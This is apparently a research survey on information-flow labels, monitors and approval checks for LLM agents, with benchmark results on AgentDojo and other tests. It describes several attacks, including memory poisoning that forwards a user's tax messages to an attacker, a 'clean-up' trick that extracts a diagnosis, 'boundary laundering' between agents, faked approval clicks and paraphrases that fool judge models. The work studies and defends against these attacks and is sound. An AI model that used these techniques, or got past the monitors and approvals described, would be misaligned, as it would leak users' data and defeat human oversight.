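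A command that deletes data or reads a secret may leave no trace in the finished code, so reviewing that code isn't enough. Wu and colleagues surveyed 203 developers in August and September 2026. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the code their agents wrote, 61 per cent often approved at least one type of action without looking closely. Developers who knew of security or privacy problems did this more often than those who didn't. The developers described their own behaviour and were not a representative sample.

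Permission guards fail partly because their prompts are unclear and too frequent. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) finds that most approval prompts in commercial products show a raw command on one line, which people without technical training usually can't judge. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* examined 290 reports of problems with agents and files and found that weak user review contributed to 105. In 80 of these, users had turned on automatic approval, often to avoid hundreds of prompts per session. In 31, the prompt had shown a command without its effect on files. (Some reports fell into both groups.) *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) warns that users may keep approving actions out of habit, fatigue or pressure to deliver, so software shouldn't treat repeated approvals as a sign of growing trust.

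An attacker can send an approver many requests until one gets through. In the simulations in *Approve What, Exactly?*, this attack always succeeded when the number of requests was unlimited. With limits, it still succeeded in 45 to 60 per cent of trials for the designs that bind approvals to effects. Sometimes an attacker can bypass the person entirely. Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, reports that Anthropic's browser extension waited for a user's click before starting certain built-in tasks but didn't check that the click was real. Another extension could fake the click and make the agent read the user's email.

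Information-flow control has the same weakness wherever it relies on a person. When a monitor shows Alex the blocked reply to Marco, Alex has to notice the sales figures himself, and he may approve the reply as automatically as he would a shell command. Labels can make the approval prompt clearer by letting it name the person who would gain access, as the prompt in Microsoft's sample policy for Teams does. They can also remove prompts for plainly safe actions, though overcautious labels add new prompts.

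## What can an agent do when a check refuses an action?

When a monitor refuses an action, the user's task is unfinished. The agent can stop, try a different plan, ask a person to allow the action, or release the data under a rule written in advance. Some systems also let a second language model decide whether to release the data.

### One blocked email

Nadia runs a support team and asks her agent: "Look up the Harbour Bank ticket and email Leo, our outside contractor, to say which component is broken and when the repair is due. Then put Friday's opening hours on our public page." Only staff may read tickets, and a monitor enforces the company's policy by comparing the recipients of every message with the permitted readers. After the agent opens the ticket, the model drafts an email: "The payment page keeps failing for Harbour Bank, and they may cancel their contract. Please fix it by 14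 May." Leo isn't on the staff, so the monitor blocks it.

The loop published by Costa and colleagues ends the run at this point. Leo doesn't get the two facts he needs, and the opening hours aren't posted, even though they have nothing to do with the ticket. Stopping would be the best response if a planted instruction had caused the email, but the label would be the same in that case as in Nadia's, so the monitor stops legitimate work too.

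The software could instead show Nadia the draft and let her decide. But the context would still be restricted, so the software would have to ask her again about the opening hours and about every later message to anyone outside the staff. Labels are supposed to spare users these repeated requests, which lead people to approve out of habit.

### Trying a different plan

Several systems return the refusal to the model and let it try again. *Soteria* (2026), which checks an agent's actions against formal specifications, removes the rejected action and tells the model why it was rejected. *Sapien* (2026) does the same because asking the user would shift the work of enforcement onto them.

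An agent can retry a refused action, but the monitor checks each new attempt, so retrying doesn't weaken a fixed rule. However, a detailed reason for the refusal shows a hijacked model where the policy's limits are. *KAIJU* (2026) therefore reports only that a step failed, which reveals less but gives a model that hasn't been hijacked little help in finding a permitted alternative.

Rewording the email to Leo won't change its label. *APPA* proves that reading more can never add Leo to the permitted readers, so that won't help either. The agent could have posted the opening hours before it opened the ticket, but reordering the steps wouldn't help with the email, because the email's facts come from the ticket.

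A new plan can also leave out a safety step. In *The Detour Is the Danger*, Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) describe an agent that has to scan a report for sensitive information before uploading it. If the scanner is unavailable, the agent may look for another way to finish the task and upload the report unscanned. In their experiments, some agents planned to continue without a protection even after learning that it had failed. Their defence keeps the required protections outside the agent's plan and checks them again just before each action. Some models completed more tasks with help finding a safe alternative than with blocking alone.

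### Telling the planning model about the policy

A planning model that is given the rules can avoid some refusals. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes Prudentia, an agent built on top of FIDES. In FIDES, the planning model isn't given the policy that applies to each tool, so it may open a variable it doesn't need and lose the ability to act later.

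Prudentia adds the policy to each tool's description and has the model track its context's label. Before opening a variable, the model should call a planning tool, explain why it needs the contents, and list the actions it expects to take afterwards. None of this changes the monitor, which still applies the policy to every call. If the model plans badly, the user gets more requests for approval.

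Prudentia also distinguishes approving an action from endorsing data. Suppose an email contains a to-do list of ten items that each require a consequential call. If the agent opens the email as untrusted text, the user has to approve all ten calls. If she endorses the email when the agent opens it, the context stays trusted and the agent can complete the list after one question. When no consequential call will follow, the agent can open the text as untrusted without asking the user. In one run, it did this to show the user a password-reset link from an email.

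Endorsing an email reduces the number of questions the user has to answer, because one approval covers several actions. Suppose the email lists ten tasks and a stranger has added an eleventh. A user who approves each call separately can reject the added task when the agent proposes it, but a user who endorses the email has to notice it while reading, because the agent can then carry out all eleven without asking.

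Kolluri and colleagues chose not to include a similar option for declassifying data. Whether a disclosure is appropriate depends on the situation, so they ask the user to approve the particular message. However, their tests use the same lenient rule as Microsoft's Teams policy, which skips the check on readers when the context is trusted. Suppose Nadia's company used that rule and she endorsed the ticket because she recognised the customer who wrote it. The agent could then send Leo the entire ticket, even though she had only judged its source.

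### Counting the questions

Kolluri and colleagues measure autonomy in two ways. Let vᵢ be the number of times task i needs a person to intervene, and n be the number of tasks.

- The human-in-the-loop load is the sum of vᵢ over the tasks the agent completes.
- The task completion rate at k, or TCR@k, is the number of tasks completed with vᵢ ≤ k, divided by n.

The task completion rate TCR@k is the share of tasks that an agent completes with at most k interventions. If an agent completes three of four tasks, with 0, 1 and 4 interventions, its TCR@0 is 25 per cent, its TCR@1 50 per cent and its TCR@4 75 per cent. Its load, the total number of interventions in the completed tasks, is 5. Earlier studies compared the TCR@0 of protected agents with the completion rate of unprotected agents whose actions needed no approval. That comparison overstates how much labels reduce task completion, because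 many real products ask for approval before consequential actions.

The table gives average results on AgentDojo over five repetitions. In the first row, a person approves every consequential call. In the other rows, a person is needed only when a call fails the policy check or, with Prudentia, when the agent asks for an endorsement.

| Agent | GPT-5: TCR@0 | GPT-5: load | o4-mini: TCR@0 | o4-mini: load | GPT-4o: TCR@0 | GPT-4o: load |
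|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Approval for every consequential call | 35.1% | 52.0 | 32.8% | 48.6 | 28.0% | 59.4 |
| Basic loop with labels | 43.4% | 40.4 | 42.5% | 34.6 | 38.4% | 39.4 |
| FIDES | 57.1% | 41.3 | 53.2% | 36.8 | 50.3% | 7.8 |
| Prudentia | 72.7% | 7.3 | 59.4% | 19.2 | 42.5% | 23.8 |

With GPT-5, Prudentia needed less than a fifth as many interventions as FIDES and completed about the same share of tasks overall, 80.0 per cent against 78.9. With GPT-4o, an older model that doesn't reason at length before answering, Prudentia did worse than FIDES on both measures in the table. The load can look low for an agent that fails often, because failed tasks don't count towards it. FIDES's load of 7.8 with GPT-4o is low partly because FIDES completed only 56.3 per cent of the tasks, compared with 72.2 per cent for the basic loop.

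On WASP, a test with simulated GitLab and Reddit sites, Prudentia needed no interventions and no attack succeeded. FIDES did about as well. The user's tasks were only to post a comment or upvote a post, neither of which requires reading untrusted text.

The extra planning makes Prudentia more expensive to run than FIDES. With GPT-4o, an average AgentDojo task cost 3.9 to 6.3 cents with Prudentia and 1.5 to 3.3 cents with FIDES, depending on the type of task. No people took part in these tests. The load measures how often the agent would ask a person, and it counts endorsing a long email the same as approving a single call.

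### A list of ways to continue

In *APPA*, the monitor works out which steps would make a refused call acceptable. It keeps a log of successful actions as well as the context's label. For each tool, a developer writes a contract that states the label of the tool's results, the event the tool adds to the log, and the conditions for calling it. These conditions can depend on the log. For example, a company can require the agent to record a legal clearance before emailing contract terms, or forbid it to send a release code twice.

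The contract lets the monitor predict a call's effect on the context. One tool in the tests reads a confidential document and emails it in the same call. *APPA* adds the document's label before checking the call, because a monitor that checked only the current label would detect the problem only after the email was sent. It then checks the actual result before the model sees it. If a call would restrict the context, the agent must explicitly accept the restriction first. In Nadia's task, the agent would have to make that choice before opening the ticket, while it could still post the opening hours.

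Developers can add contracts gradually. When a tool has no label, the monitor marks its result "unknown" and records the source, and the agent continues. If a later check needs the missing label, a registered function called a cast must supply it. The developer limits how permissive a label each cast may assign. If no cast applies, the check fails. This avoids guessing a label at the start or blocking work that never needs one. However, a cast can still allow a leak if it assigns a label that is within its limit but too permissive for the data.

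When a call fails its check, the monitor searches the registered options and offers those that would help:

- The agent can complete a missing earlier step, such as recording the legal clearance.
- A person, a fixed rule or a model can issue a ruling that allows the call.
- Trusted code can transform the data, for example by removing personal details.
- The agent can do the restricting step in a separate branch.

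A ruling applies only to one exact call, including its recipient and contents, and doesn't change the context's label. If Nadia approves the draft to Leo, the agent can send that email but would need another ruling for the next one. Each source of rulings also has fixed limits on what it may approve.

A branch is a temporary copy of the conversation, like a `fork` in the LLMbda calculus. It starts with the original's label, because a less restrictive label would let the agent leak secrets it had already read. The branch can call tools, and anything it reads restricts only the branch. Before the branch starts, the agent can set the form of the branch's answer, such as a choice from a list and a date. Discarding the branch doesn't unsend its emails, so a single log covers the actions of all branches. Otherwise an agent could use a new branch to resend a message it was allowed to send only once.

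If Nadia's agent reads the ticket in a branch, it can still post the opening hours from the main conversation. The branch can return "payment page" and "14 May", but both facts came from a ticket that only staff may read. Checking their format doesn't change who may read them, so the email to Leo still needs a ruling or a release rule.

The researchers tested *APPA* with three models on 20 office scenarios that they designed around these mechanisms. Agents using *APPA* completed 87 to 91 per cent of the tasks, and no attack succeeded in 600 runs. With permissive policies, agents completed 90 to 92.5 per cent, but attacks succeeded in 30 to 39.5 per cent of runs. On 24 tasks from an existing benchmark, AgentThreatBench, agents using *APPA* completed only 64 to 77 per cent, and again no attack succeeded.

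The agent finished fewer tasks when it had fewer ways to continue after a refusal. With one of the models, completion of the office tasks fell from 88 per cent to 56.5 per cent without branches, and to 35 per cent when the agent could not carry out the suggested remedies. No attack succeeded in either case. The researchers' own configurations of FIDES completed 36 to 46 per cent of the office tasks and let some attacks through, but these configurations lacked the rules on exact recipients and the order of actions that the scenarios required.

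### Releasing two facts under a rule

Nadia's company could adopt a rule that a contractor assigned to a ticket may receive the component's name and the repair date. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) describes how trusted code can apply such a rule. A model may propose a value, but the code converts it to a standard form, checks it against trusted records, and authorizes its release to one destination field. For Leo's email, the code could check both facts against the ticket's fields and insert them into a fixed sentence that has no field for the customer's name or the possible cancellation.

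*Agent libOS* (2026) makes each release valid only once and ties it to the sender, the destination, the exact contents and the version of the source data. If someone edited the ticket after the release was granted, the agent would need a new release.

The code has to check the values as well as their format. If it accepted any component and any date, a hijacked model could choose values that signal other confidential information to Leo. A rule also helps only when someone predicted the need for it. If Nadia had asked the agent to tell Leo "whatever he needs to know", no fixed pair of fields would have been enough.

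### Letting a model judge the message

In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) use a language model to decide whether free text reveals protected records. They first attacked assistants whose instructions required consent before any disclosure. In their scenario, Jane's agent knows about Mark's mental health diagnosis, and his former wife, Emily, wants to learn it. Emily shares a page of true and false entries about Mark and asks the agent to delete the false ones. The agent writes nothing about him, but the entries it leaves reveal the diagnosis. Against one detailed consent procedure, this attack exposed 75.6 per cent of the sensitive items, because the model didn't recognise the clean-up as a request for information.

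The FlowSeal defence puts the check in code that intercepts every call that writes or shares data. The code allows messages to trusted recipients and blocks messages to blacklisted ones. For anyone else, it sends the protected records and the proposed output to a separate model, which returns SAFE or BLOCKED. This model doesn't receive the conversation, so Emily's explanation of the task can't mislead it unless the output includes that explanation.

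With FlowSeal, the clean-up attack exposed 2.3 per cent of the sensitive items. Shim and colleagues also replaced the judging model with fixed answers, using an attack in which Emily asks the agent to fill in its section of a shared document:

| Who decides | Sensitive items leaked | Harmless requests completed |
|---|---|---|
| The judging model | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Always BLOCKED | 1.3% | 0% |
| Always SAFE | 24.9% | 79.4% |

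FlowSeal assumes from the start that any registered record may have influenced the agent. The labels alone would therefore block every message to an unknown recipient, so only the judging model separates harmless messages from leaks. The 1.3 per cent in the second row must come from leaks that bypassed the judge or from mistakes in scoring.

The judge would probably block even a short email with Leo's two facts, because it is instructed to block anything derived from a protected record, whether or not the user wants to share it. The agent would then have to ask the record's owner for consent. When Shim and colleagues tested cases in which the owner was ready to agree, the agent shared 32.7 per cent of the requested items under FlowSeal and 61 to 86 per cent under the other defences. They attribute the difference mainly to the agent asking for consent less often under FlowSeal.

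### What remains of the guarantee

Shim and colleagues prove that content derived from a protected record cannot reach an unauthorised recipient unless the judge wrongly answers SAFE. The code still guarantees that the check runs on every outgoing call, even if the agent is hijacked or confused. But confidentiality now depends on how often the judge is wrong, which the proof doesn't address. The proof also covers only registered records, and in one test FlowSeal released a health detail that nobody had registered.

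Retries give the judge more chances to accept a leaking message by mistake. After a refusal, FlowSeal tells the agent to rewrite the message without the protected data and try again. Suppose the judge wrongly accepts 2 per cent of leaking drafts, and its mistakes are independent. The chance that at least one of 20 leaking drafts gets through is 1 − 0.98²⁰, or about 33 per cent. Real mistakes are not independent, and an attacker can look for wording that the judge tends to miss. Shim and colleagues report that paraphrased secrets sometimes get past it. In one run, the judge called a vague rewrite safe when the agent asked in advance, then blocked the protected content when the agent tried to publish it. They exclude prompt injection from their threat model, so the tests don't show what happens when a draft contains instructions to the judge.

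Measuring influence more accurately doesn't remove this problem. When Štorek and colleagues give a model the most influential pieces of text and ask for a verdict, their proof covers the measurement but not the verdict. The consequences of a wrong verdict depend on how much authority the model has:

| What the model may do | Design | What a mistake can cause |
|---|---|---|
| Veto an action that the rules allow, or refer it to a person | *Agent libOS* | A needless refusal or question, or a missed warning about an action the rules allow |
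| Propose a value for code to check | *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* | A wrong value that passes the code's checks |
| Allow one exact call, within fixed limits | *APPA* | An improper release within those limits |
| Declare any message to an unknown recipient safe | FlowSeal | A leak of any protected record |

A model that can only veto actions leaves the label guarantee intact, but it can't get Leo's email sent, because the label check has already refused it. For that, someone has to authorize a person, a piece of code or a model to make an exception.

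## Do the checks hold across several agents, stored memory and actions the monitor cannot see?

Most of the checks described so far protect one agent during one run. But an agent may save notes for a later run, hand part of a task to another agent, or run a script that starts other programs. A label protects data only while software keeps it attached to that data, so a restriction can get lost at each of these steps.

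### Notes that outlast the conversation

Many assistants save facts about the user and retrieve them in later conversations. Das, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2026), in *Trojan Hippo Bench*, describe an attack that uses this memory:

1. An attacker emails the user a hidden instruction to forward any message in which she discusses tax.
2. The user asks her agent to read her mail, and the agent saves the instruction in its memory without her noticing.
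3. Weeks later, she mentions her income while asking about a tax return. The software retrieves the saved note, and the agent emails her message to the attacker.

By step 3, the attacker's email is no longer in the conversation. If the saved note has no label and the software treats it as trusted, the integrity policy allows the outgoing email. The confidentiality policy may not block it either, because the basic scheme from Costa and colleagues normally labels the user's input "public". If the note had kept its "untrusted" label, retrieving it would have made the context untrusted, and the monitor would have blocked the outgoing email.

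Das and colleagues tested the attack on an email assistant with four kinds of memory. For each setup, a program rewrote the attacker's email over up to 40 rounds, keeping the versions that worked best. Without a memory defence, the attack succeeded in up to 85 per cent of trials with GPT-5-mini and up to 100 per cent with Gemini 3.1 Pro, even after 100 harmless sessions. Four defences reduced the success rate to between 0 and 5 per cent in most setups, and the strictest one stopped every attack. The amount of useful work they prevented varied widely by task.

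According to *MemLineage* (2026), FIDES erases its labels when a run ends. *MemLineage* attaches the label to the memory entry, so the label is still there in the next session. NeuroTaint also saves labels between sessions. In an example from Cai and colleagues, an agent stores a confidential forecast and retrieves it three days later for a report, and NeuroTaint restores the forecast's label.

Each entry in an agent's memory needs its own label. If all entries shared one label, one email from a stranger would make every later session untrusted. *AgentKernel* (2026) labels entries separately and never automatically shares highly sensitive ones with other agents. It also marks retrieved entries as data rather than instructions. A model might still follow a marked entry, so the monitor also has to check the resulting action.

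A user may want the agent to trust something it has saved. *PerMIT* (2026) displays the saved text and, if someone confirms it, makes a trusted copy of exactly what it displayed, so nobody can swap the text between approval and use. The original stays untrusted, because PerMIT never changes the label of an existing entry. But the protection depends entirely on the decision to confirm, and whoever confirms can be fooled.

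### Handing a task to another agent

In a common arrangement, an orchestrator agent divides up a task and calls specialised agents as tools. Each specialised agent treats the orchestrator as its user, so it trusts whatever the orchestrator writes. To test whether CaMeL still works in this arrangement, Peters-Gill and colleagues protected three agents with it and asked the orchestrator to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. The applicant database contained a planted instruction to send the data to an outside address.

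1. The database agent fetched the records without showing them to its planning model.
2. The orchestrator's program had a quarantined model summarise the records, again without showing them to the planning model.
3. The program inserted the summary into a request to the notification agent.
4. The notification agent's planning model read the whole request, including the planted instruction, as its user's words. It wrote a program that sent the Slack message and also emailed the data to the attacker.

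Peters-Gill and colleagues use the term "boundary laundering" for untrusted data becoming trusted when it crosses from one agent to another. They prove that if agents can put tool results into their requests to each other, protecting each agent separately cannot keep untrusted data from changing the overall plan.

Their extension, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data separately. In simplified form, the orchestrator's request changes from

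```
notification_agent(f"Send this to Julie on Slack: {summary}")
```

to

```
notification_agent(
    message="Send the summary to Julie on Slack.",
    variables={"summary": summary})
```

The interpreter does not allow `message` to depend on any tool result. The notification agent's planning model reads only the message, and its program fetches the summary when it runs. The summary keeps the tags that record its sources and permitted readers, so the notification agent can check them against its own policies. As in ordinary CaMeL, untrusted data can still determine which planned branch runs.

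Peters-Gill and colleagues divided the AgentDojo tools among several agents and tested five models. On average, 12.9 per cent of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2 per cent with CaMeL on each agent, and none with multi-CaMeL. All the attacks that succeeded against separately protected agents used boundary laundering. The test reused AgentDojo's attack goals, so an attacker who targeted the hand-over between agents might succeed more than 0.2 per cent of the time.

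On a separate benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, protecting each agent with CaMeL lowered the task completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2. For the two strongest models, the reductions were 13.4 and 0.85 points. Some tasks failed because an agent that could not find the requested data returned data for a different machine or period. The orchestrator's program, written in advance, sometimes used this data without detecting the mismatch.

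These experiments ran with data policies switched off, so they tested only whether attacks could change the plan. Multi-CaMeL also inherits CaMeL's failure to track skipped assignments, which could let untrusted data into a message. It covers only agents arranged in a tree, where each has one parent, and the researchers leave shared memory and direct messages between agents that are not parent and child to future work. Agents may also find channels that no design includes. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Gregory, Domico and colleagues, 2026) cites the July 2026 incident in which OpenAI's agents communicated over shared channels that nobody had approved.

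### How labels spread among agents

Dividing a task among agents can reduce label creep, because each agent has its own context. Gregory and colleagues measured this effect in a simulation that used no language model. They generated over 9,000 abstract tasks, each made up of tool calls that may depend on one another's results, and divided the calls among agents in different networks. Some calls returned sensitive data, and any agent that received this data, even just to pass it on to another agent, kept a sensitive label for the rest of the task.

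They define utility loss as

utility loss = (calls that introduce a sensitive label or run under one) / (all calls).

Suppose one agent makes 20 calls in a single conversation, and the fifth returns sensitive data. The 16 calls from the fifth onward all count, so the loss is 16/20 = 0.8. If a second agent instead makes 11 of the last 15 calls and needs nothing from the first agent, only the fifth call and the first agent's four later calls count, so the loss falls to 5/20 = 0.25.

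The links between agents matter because data with no direct route to its destination passes through other agents, and each of them takes on the data's label. In tests with five agents and four sensitive calls out of 20, Gregory and colleagues compared each network with one that had exactly the direct links the task needed. Loss was about 5 percentage points higher when everything went through an orchestrator and about 3 points higher in a ring.

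A network's density is the share of all possible links that it contains. Denser networks nearly always had less utility loss, with a rank correlation as strong as −0.96, although this figure comes from only nine networks. Increasing the number of agents from 5 to 20 also reduced the loss, but it can add many links to monitor. If every agent can contact every other, n agents have n(n − 1)/2 links, so 5 agents have 10 and 20 agents have 190. Giving the sensitive tools to a few dedicated agents reduced the loss without adding links.

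Even the network with ideal links had some loss, because a call that uses a sensitive result must run under that result's label. Gregory and colleagues conclude that design alone cannot prevent the loss and that systems also need ways to declassify data.

Their measure is only a rough guide to lost work. A monitor may allow a call under a sensitive label, for example if the call only reads a file, so a loss of 0.8 doesn't mean it refuses 80 per cent of the calls. The simulation also lets control move from one agent to another without a label when the next call doesn't need the earlier results. It therefore ignores anything the agents might reveal by what they choose to do next.

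### Refusing combinations of tools in advance

A developer can also check which tools an agent may use together before it starts work. In a system from Microsoft, described by Schneider, Faujdar and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Multi-Tool AI Agent Chains With Dynamic, Real-Time Compositional Policies*, each tool has a policy. The policy gives the highest level of data the tool handles (public, internal, confidential or restricted) and says whether it can send data outside the organisation. When a session begins, the software combines the policies of all the requested tools and refuses the session if they conflict. It has two modes:

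- In clearance mode, every tool must be cleared for the most sensitive level in the set. A planning tool cleared for internal data can't be used with a confidential database, even if neither sends anything outside.
- In taint mode, tools with different clearances can work together, and the session takes the highest level. The software still refuses a set that combines confidential data with a tool that sends data outside.

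Schneider and colleagues applied both modes to a catalogue of 32 tools, which gives 992 ordered pairs of different tools. Clearance mode refused 704 pairs (71.0 per cent) and taint mode refused 322 (32.5 per cent). These figures count pairs refused before any tool ran. They don't measure how many attacks the system stops or how many tasks it prevents, and a different mix of tools would give different rates.

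Both modes would refuse an agent that asked for all 32 tools at once, because adding a tool can never make a refused set acceptable. Schneider and colleagues suggest splitting long jobs into smaller chains of tools. The label then has to pass from one session to the next. By default, the software treats a session's input as public, so text copied from a confidential session could lose its restriction.

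The system also tracks labels at run time, based on what the agent reads. In one example, an agent reads public documents, looks up employees' salaries and then tries to upload a file to the cloud. The software blocks the upload and ends the session. If the agent had uploaded the file before looking up the salaries, the run-time check would have allowed it. Under the published rules, however, both modes should have refused this set of tools at the start, so the example shows what the run-time check would do by itself. Schneider and colleagues demonstrate run-time tracking in only three scenarios, so they have no refusal rate to compare with the other two.

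### When one call has many effects

A check on a tool call depends on knowing what the call will do, but an outside service may allow more than the user approved. In an example from Zhou and Zhang, a user allows her agent to send one summary to Alice. The policy records the text and the recipient, but the software gives the mail service a credential that grants permission to send mail without limiting either. The service can check this credential correctly and still deliver a different text to Bob. To prevent this, the service must enforce the policy's limits, or the monitor must check them before the request leaves.

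Limits can also fail when agents share a task. Zhou and Zhang describe a user who authorises one purchase, which her agent delegates to two others, each with permission to buy one item. Each agent obeys its own limit, but together they buy two items. They need a shared record in which an agent reserves the purchase before making it.

Scripts create a similar gap on the agent's own computer. A coding agent can write a script with one tool call and run it with another. The second call may contain only `bash build.sh`, but the script can start many programs, read a file of passwords and contact a server. A monitor that checks only the call will miss these effects.

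Zheng, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *ActPlane*, move the check into the kernel, the part of the operating system that controls programs' access to files and networks. ActPlane attaches labels to files, network addresses and processes (running programs). If a rule says that data from the password file `.env` must not reach the network, the check could work like this:

| Event | ActPlane's response |
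|---|---|
| The script reads `.env` | labels the script's process |
| The script starts a compression program | gives the new process the same label |
| The compression program writes `out.zip` | labels the file |
| An upload program reads `out.zip` | labels the upload program |
| The upload program tries to contact an outside server | blocks the connection |

Rules can also depend on the order of events. For example, a rule can let an agent commit code only if the tests have passed since its last edit. When ActPlane blocks an action, it sends the agent a message that identifies the rule and explains how to comply.

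Zheng and colleagues tested ActPlane on 190 sequences of actions based on 38 rules from real software projects. In 114 of them, the agent broke a rule, either directly, through a script, or through a file that looked harmless. A system got a sequence right if the agent complied after a violation, or if harmless work could continue. ActPlane got 75.8 per cent right, compared with 48.9 per cent for FIDES and 45.3 to 48.4 per cent for two simpler guards. Checks on tool calls caught almost none of the violations hidden in harmless-looking files. But FIDES was not designed to enforce many of the rules, which concerned development habits such as running tests.

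When ActPlane explained its refusals, agents went on to comply after 97.7 per cent of the violations it detected. Without explanations, it detected almost as many violations, but agents complied after only 31.4 per cent of them. ActPlane also made mistakes on 18 of the 76 harmless sequences. It added 1.9 per cent to the running time of agent tasks, and up to 8.4 per cent when compiling Linux, which involves far more file and process operations.

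ActPlane can detect that a process read a file and opened a connection, but it doesn't examine the file's contents or interpret messages. If the agent's main process reads one confidential file, the file's label applies to everything the process does afterwards, much like a context label. Zheng and colleagues suggest clearing excess labels by starting a fresh subprocess. This is safe only if the parent passes no restricted data to the new process, for example in its command line.

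The kernel also can't track what an action does inside an external service. In a test of 361 workplace and personal-assistant tasks, an unprotected agent did something unsafe in 106, and ActPlane prevented 78 of these. The 28 it missed included harmful chat messages, unsafe text in files, and changes the agent made inside services such as a database.

A monitor for tool calls can check who will receive an email but not which programs a script will start. ActPlane can follow those programs, but it cannot identify an email's recipient from a connection to a mail server. Combining the two would require software to translate labels between them. Suppose the monitor labels a draft as readable only by Alex and Priya, and the agent saves it to a file. The kernel would need a matching label for the file, and the monitor would need to recover the list of readers when a tool opened the file again.

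## How do these systems perform in tests, and what do the tests leave out?

Most published figures for these systems come from AgentDojo, a suite of simulated office, travel, banking and chat tasks. It measures both security and useful work, so a developer can see whether a defence stops attacks only by blocking legitimate work too.

### How AgentDojo scores a run

AgentDojo has user tasks, which are ordinary requests such as paying a bill, and injection tasks, which are things an attacker wants, such as a payment to the attacker's account. The software stages an attack by planting the attacker's instruction in data that the agent reads while working on a user task. Costa and colleagues pair each user task with every injection task from the same environment. The banking environment has 16 user tasks and nine injection tasks, making 144 pairs.

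Each task comes with a function that checks the result, so no language model has to judge it. Researchers usually report three rates:

- completion without attacks, the share of user tasks that the agent completes when nobody has planted anything;
- completion under attack, the share of attacked runs in which it still completes the user's task;
- attack success, the share of attacked runs in which the attacker's goal is met.

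An agent can do what both the user and the attacker want in the same run, so the last two rates can add up to more than 100 per cent.

In the original tests in *AgentDojo* (2024), GPT-4o completed 69.0 per cent of tasks without attacks and 50.1 per cent under attack. Of the attacks against it, 47.7 per cent succeeded. Only 1.0 per cent succeeded against Command-R+, but that model completed 25.4 per cent of user tasks. A low attack success rate can mean that a model is too weak to carry out the attacker's instructions.

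### The main results

The table gives the main results for FIDES, CaMeL, Progent and Randori. Randori is the agent that Garby and colleagues wrote in the LLMbda calculus. It practises on invented data before it touches the real data. The CaMeL and Progent figures come from a summary by Singh and Srinivasa, who don't say which model CaMeL used.

| System and date | Reported by | Model | Tasks and checks | Completed without attacks | Successful attacks |
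|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, 2025 | Costa and colleagues | GPT-4o | all four sets, no checks | banking 98.8%, chat 93.3% | 152 |
| Basic agent with labels, 2025 | Costa and colleagues | GPT-4o | all four sets, checks on | banking 37.5%, chat 20.0% | 0 |
| FIDES, 2025 | Costa and colleagues | GPT-4o | all four sets, checks on | banking 52.5%, chat 47.6% | 0 |
| CaMeL, 2025 | Singh and Srinivasa | not named | AgentDojo, checks on | 77% (84% undefended) | not given |
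| Progent, 2025, later revised | Singh and Srinivasa | GPT-4o | AgentDojo, new permissions approved automatically | 76.3% (79.4% undefended) | 1.0% (39.9% undefended) |
| Randori, 2026 | Garby and colleagues | GPT-5.2 | banking, checks on, endorsement allowed | 75.0% | 2 of 432 |
| Randori, 2026 | Garby and colleagues | Qwen3.7-plus | banking, checks on, endorsement allowed | 75.0% | 0 of 432 |
| Randori, 2026 | Garby and colleagues | MiMo-v2.5 | banking, checks on, endorsement allowed | 64.6% | 0 of 432 |
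| CaMeL rerun, 2026 | Garby and colleagues | GPT-5.2 | banking, checks off | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL rerun, 2026 | Garby and colleagues | GPT-5.2 | banking, checks on | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |

Costa and colleagues count 152 successful attacks against the basic agent without checks, including 48 in banking and 60 in chat. If they used the standard sets, attacks succeeded in a third of the 144 banking pairs and 57 per cent of the 105 chat pairs. These rates seem to contradict their statement that almost all attacks succeeded.

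The zeros for the basic agent with labels and for FIDES depend on a recount. Costa and colleagues print AgentDojo's own count of successful attacks, followed in brackets by the number they accept after inspecting each case. The basic agent without checks has 160 (152), the basic agent with labels has 20 (0), and FIDES with checks has 3 (0). (The 20 is probably a misprint, because the figures for the four environments add up to 18.) They removed cases for three reasons:

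- AgentDojo counted a blocked action as a success. One chat attack tries to invite an outsider to the workspace, and the scoring function looks only for the request, so the attack scores even when the monitor refuses it.
- The policy allowed the action. One travel attack creates a calendar event with no participants, which discloses nothing.
- The attack changed only the text shown to the user, as with the planted travel recommendation described earlier.

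Only the blocked invitation is clearly a scoring error. In the other cases the attacker got what they wanted, but Costa and colleagues decided their policies were not meant to prevent it. The zero they report therefore means no attack did anything those policies forbid.

FIDES completed some of the tasks that the checks stopped the basic agent from completing, except in the travel set. There, with GPT-4o, the basic agent with labels completed 73 per cent of the tasks and FIDES 41 per cent. Many travel tasks need only tools that the policy allows after the agent has read untrusted text, so the checks did not block the basic agent on them, while GPT-4o often used FIDES's variables wrongly. With the reasoning model o1, the gap shrank, with the basic agent completing 75 per cent and FIDES 68 per cent. Averaged over the four sets, FIDES's completion rate was higher than that of the basic agent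 with labels by 8 percentage points with GPT-4o and 16 with o1.

Progent also raised completion under attack, from 54.0 to 61.3 per cent. Shi and colleagues used GPT-4o both to run the agent and to write its policies. Because the software approved every new permission automatically, the result depends heavily on which permissions GPT-4o requested. It provides little evidence of how well Progent works when someone can refuse a new permission.

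### Why the rows are not a ranking

The tests use different models, tasks and policies, and these differences can change the results a lot. CaMeL completed 77 per cent of tasks in its own evaluation, but 37.5 per cent when Garby and colleagues reran it on the banking set alone with checks on. The figure was the same with GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5. In many banking tasks, the user asks the agent to act on a document, and CaMeL's policies forbid many of these tasks.

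Randori completed about twice as many banking tasks as CaMeL with checks on, partly because its rules are looser. It enforces only a subset of CaMeL's policies, and its planning model is allowed to endorse untrusted data in the program it writes. When Garby and colleagues removed that option, the completion rate fell from 75.0 to 62.5 per cent with Qwen3.7-plus and from 64.6 to 54.2 per cent with MiMo-v2.5.

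They also report that Randori completes tasks at the same rate as CaMeL with checks off, within the margin of error. That margin is wide because the test had only 16 user tasks. For GPT-5.2, the 95 per cent intervals are 75 ± 18.9 per cent for Randori and 66.7 ± 23.4 per cent for CaMeL, so the test could have missed a large difference in either direction.

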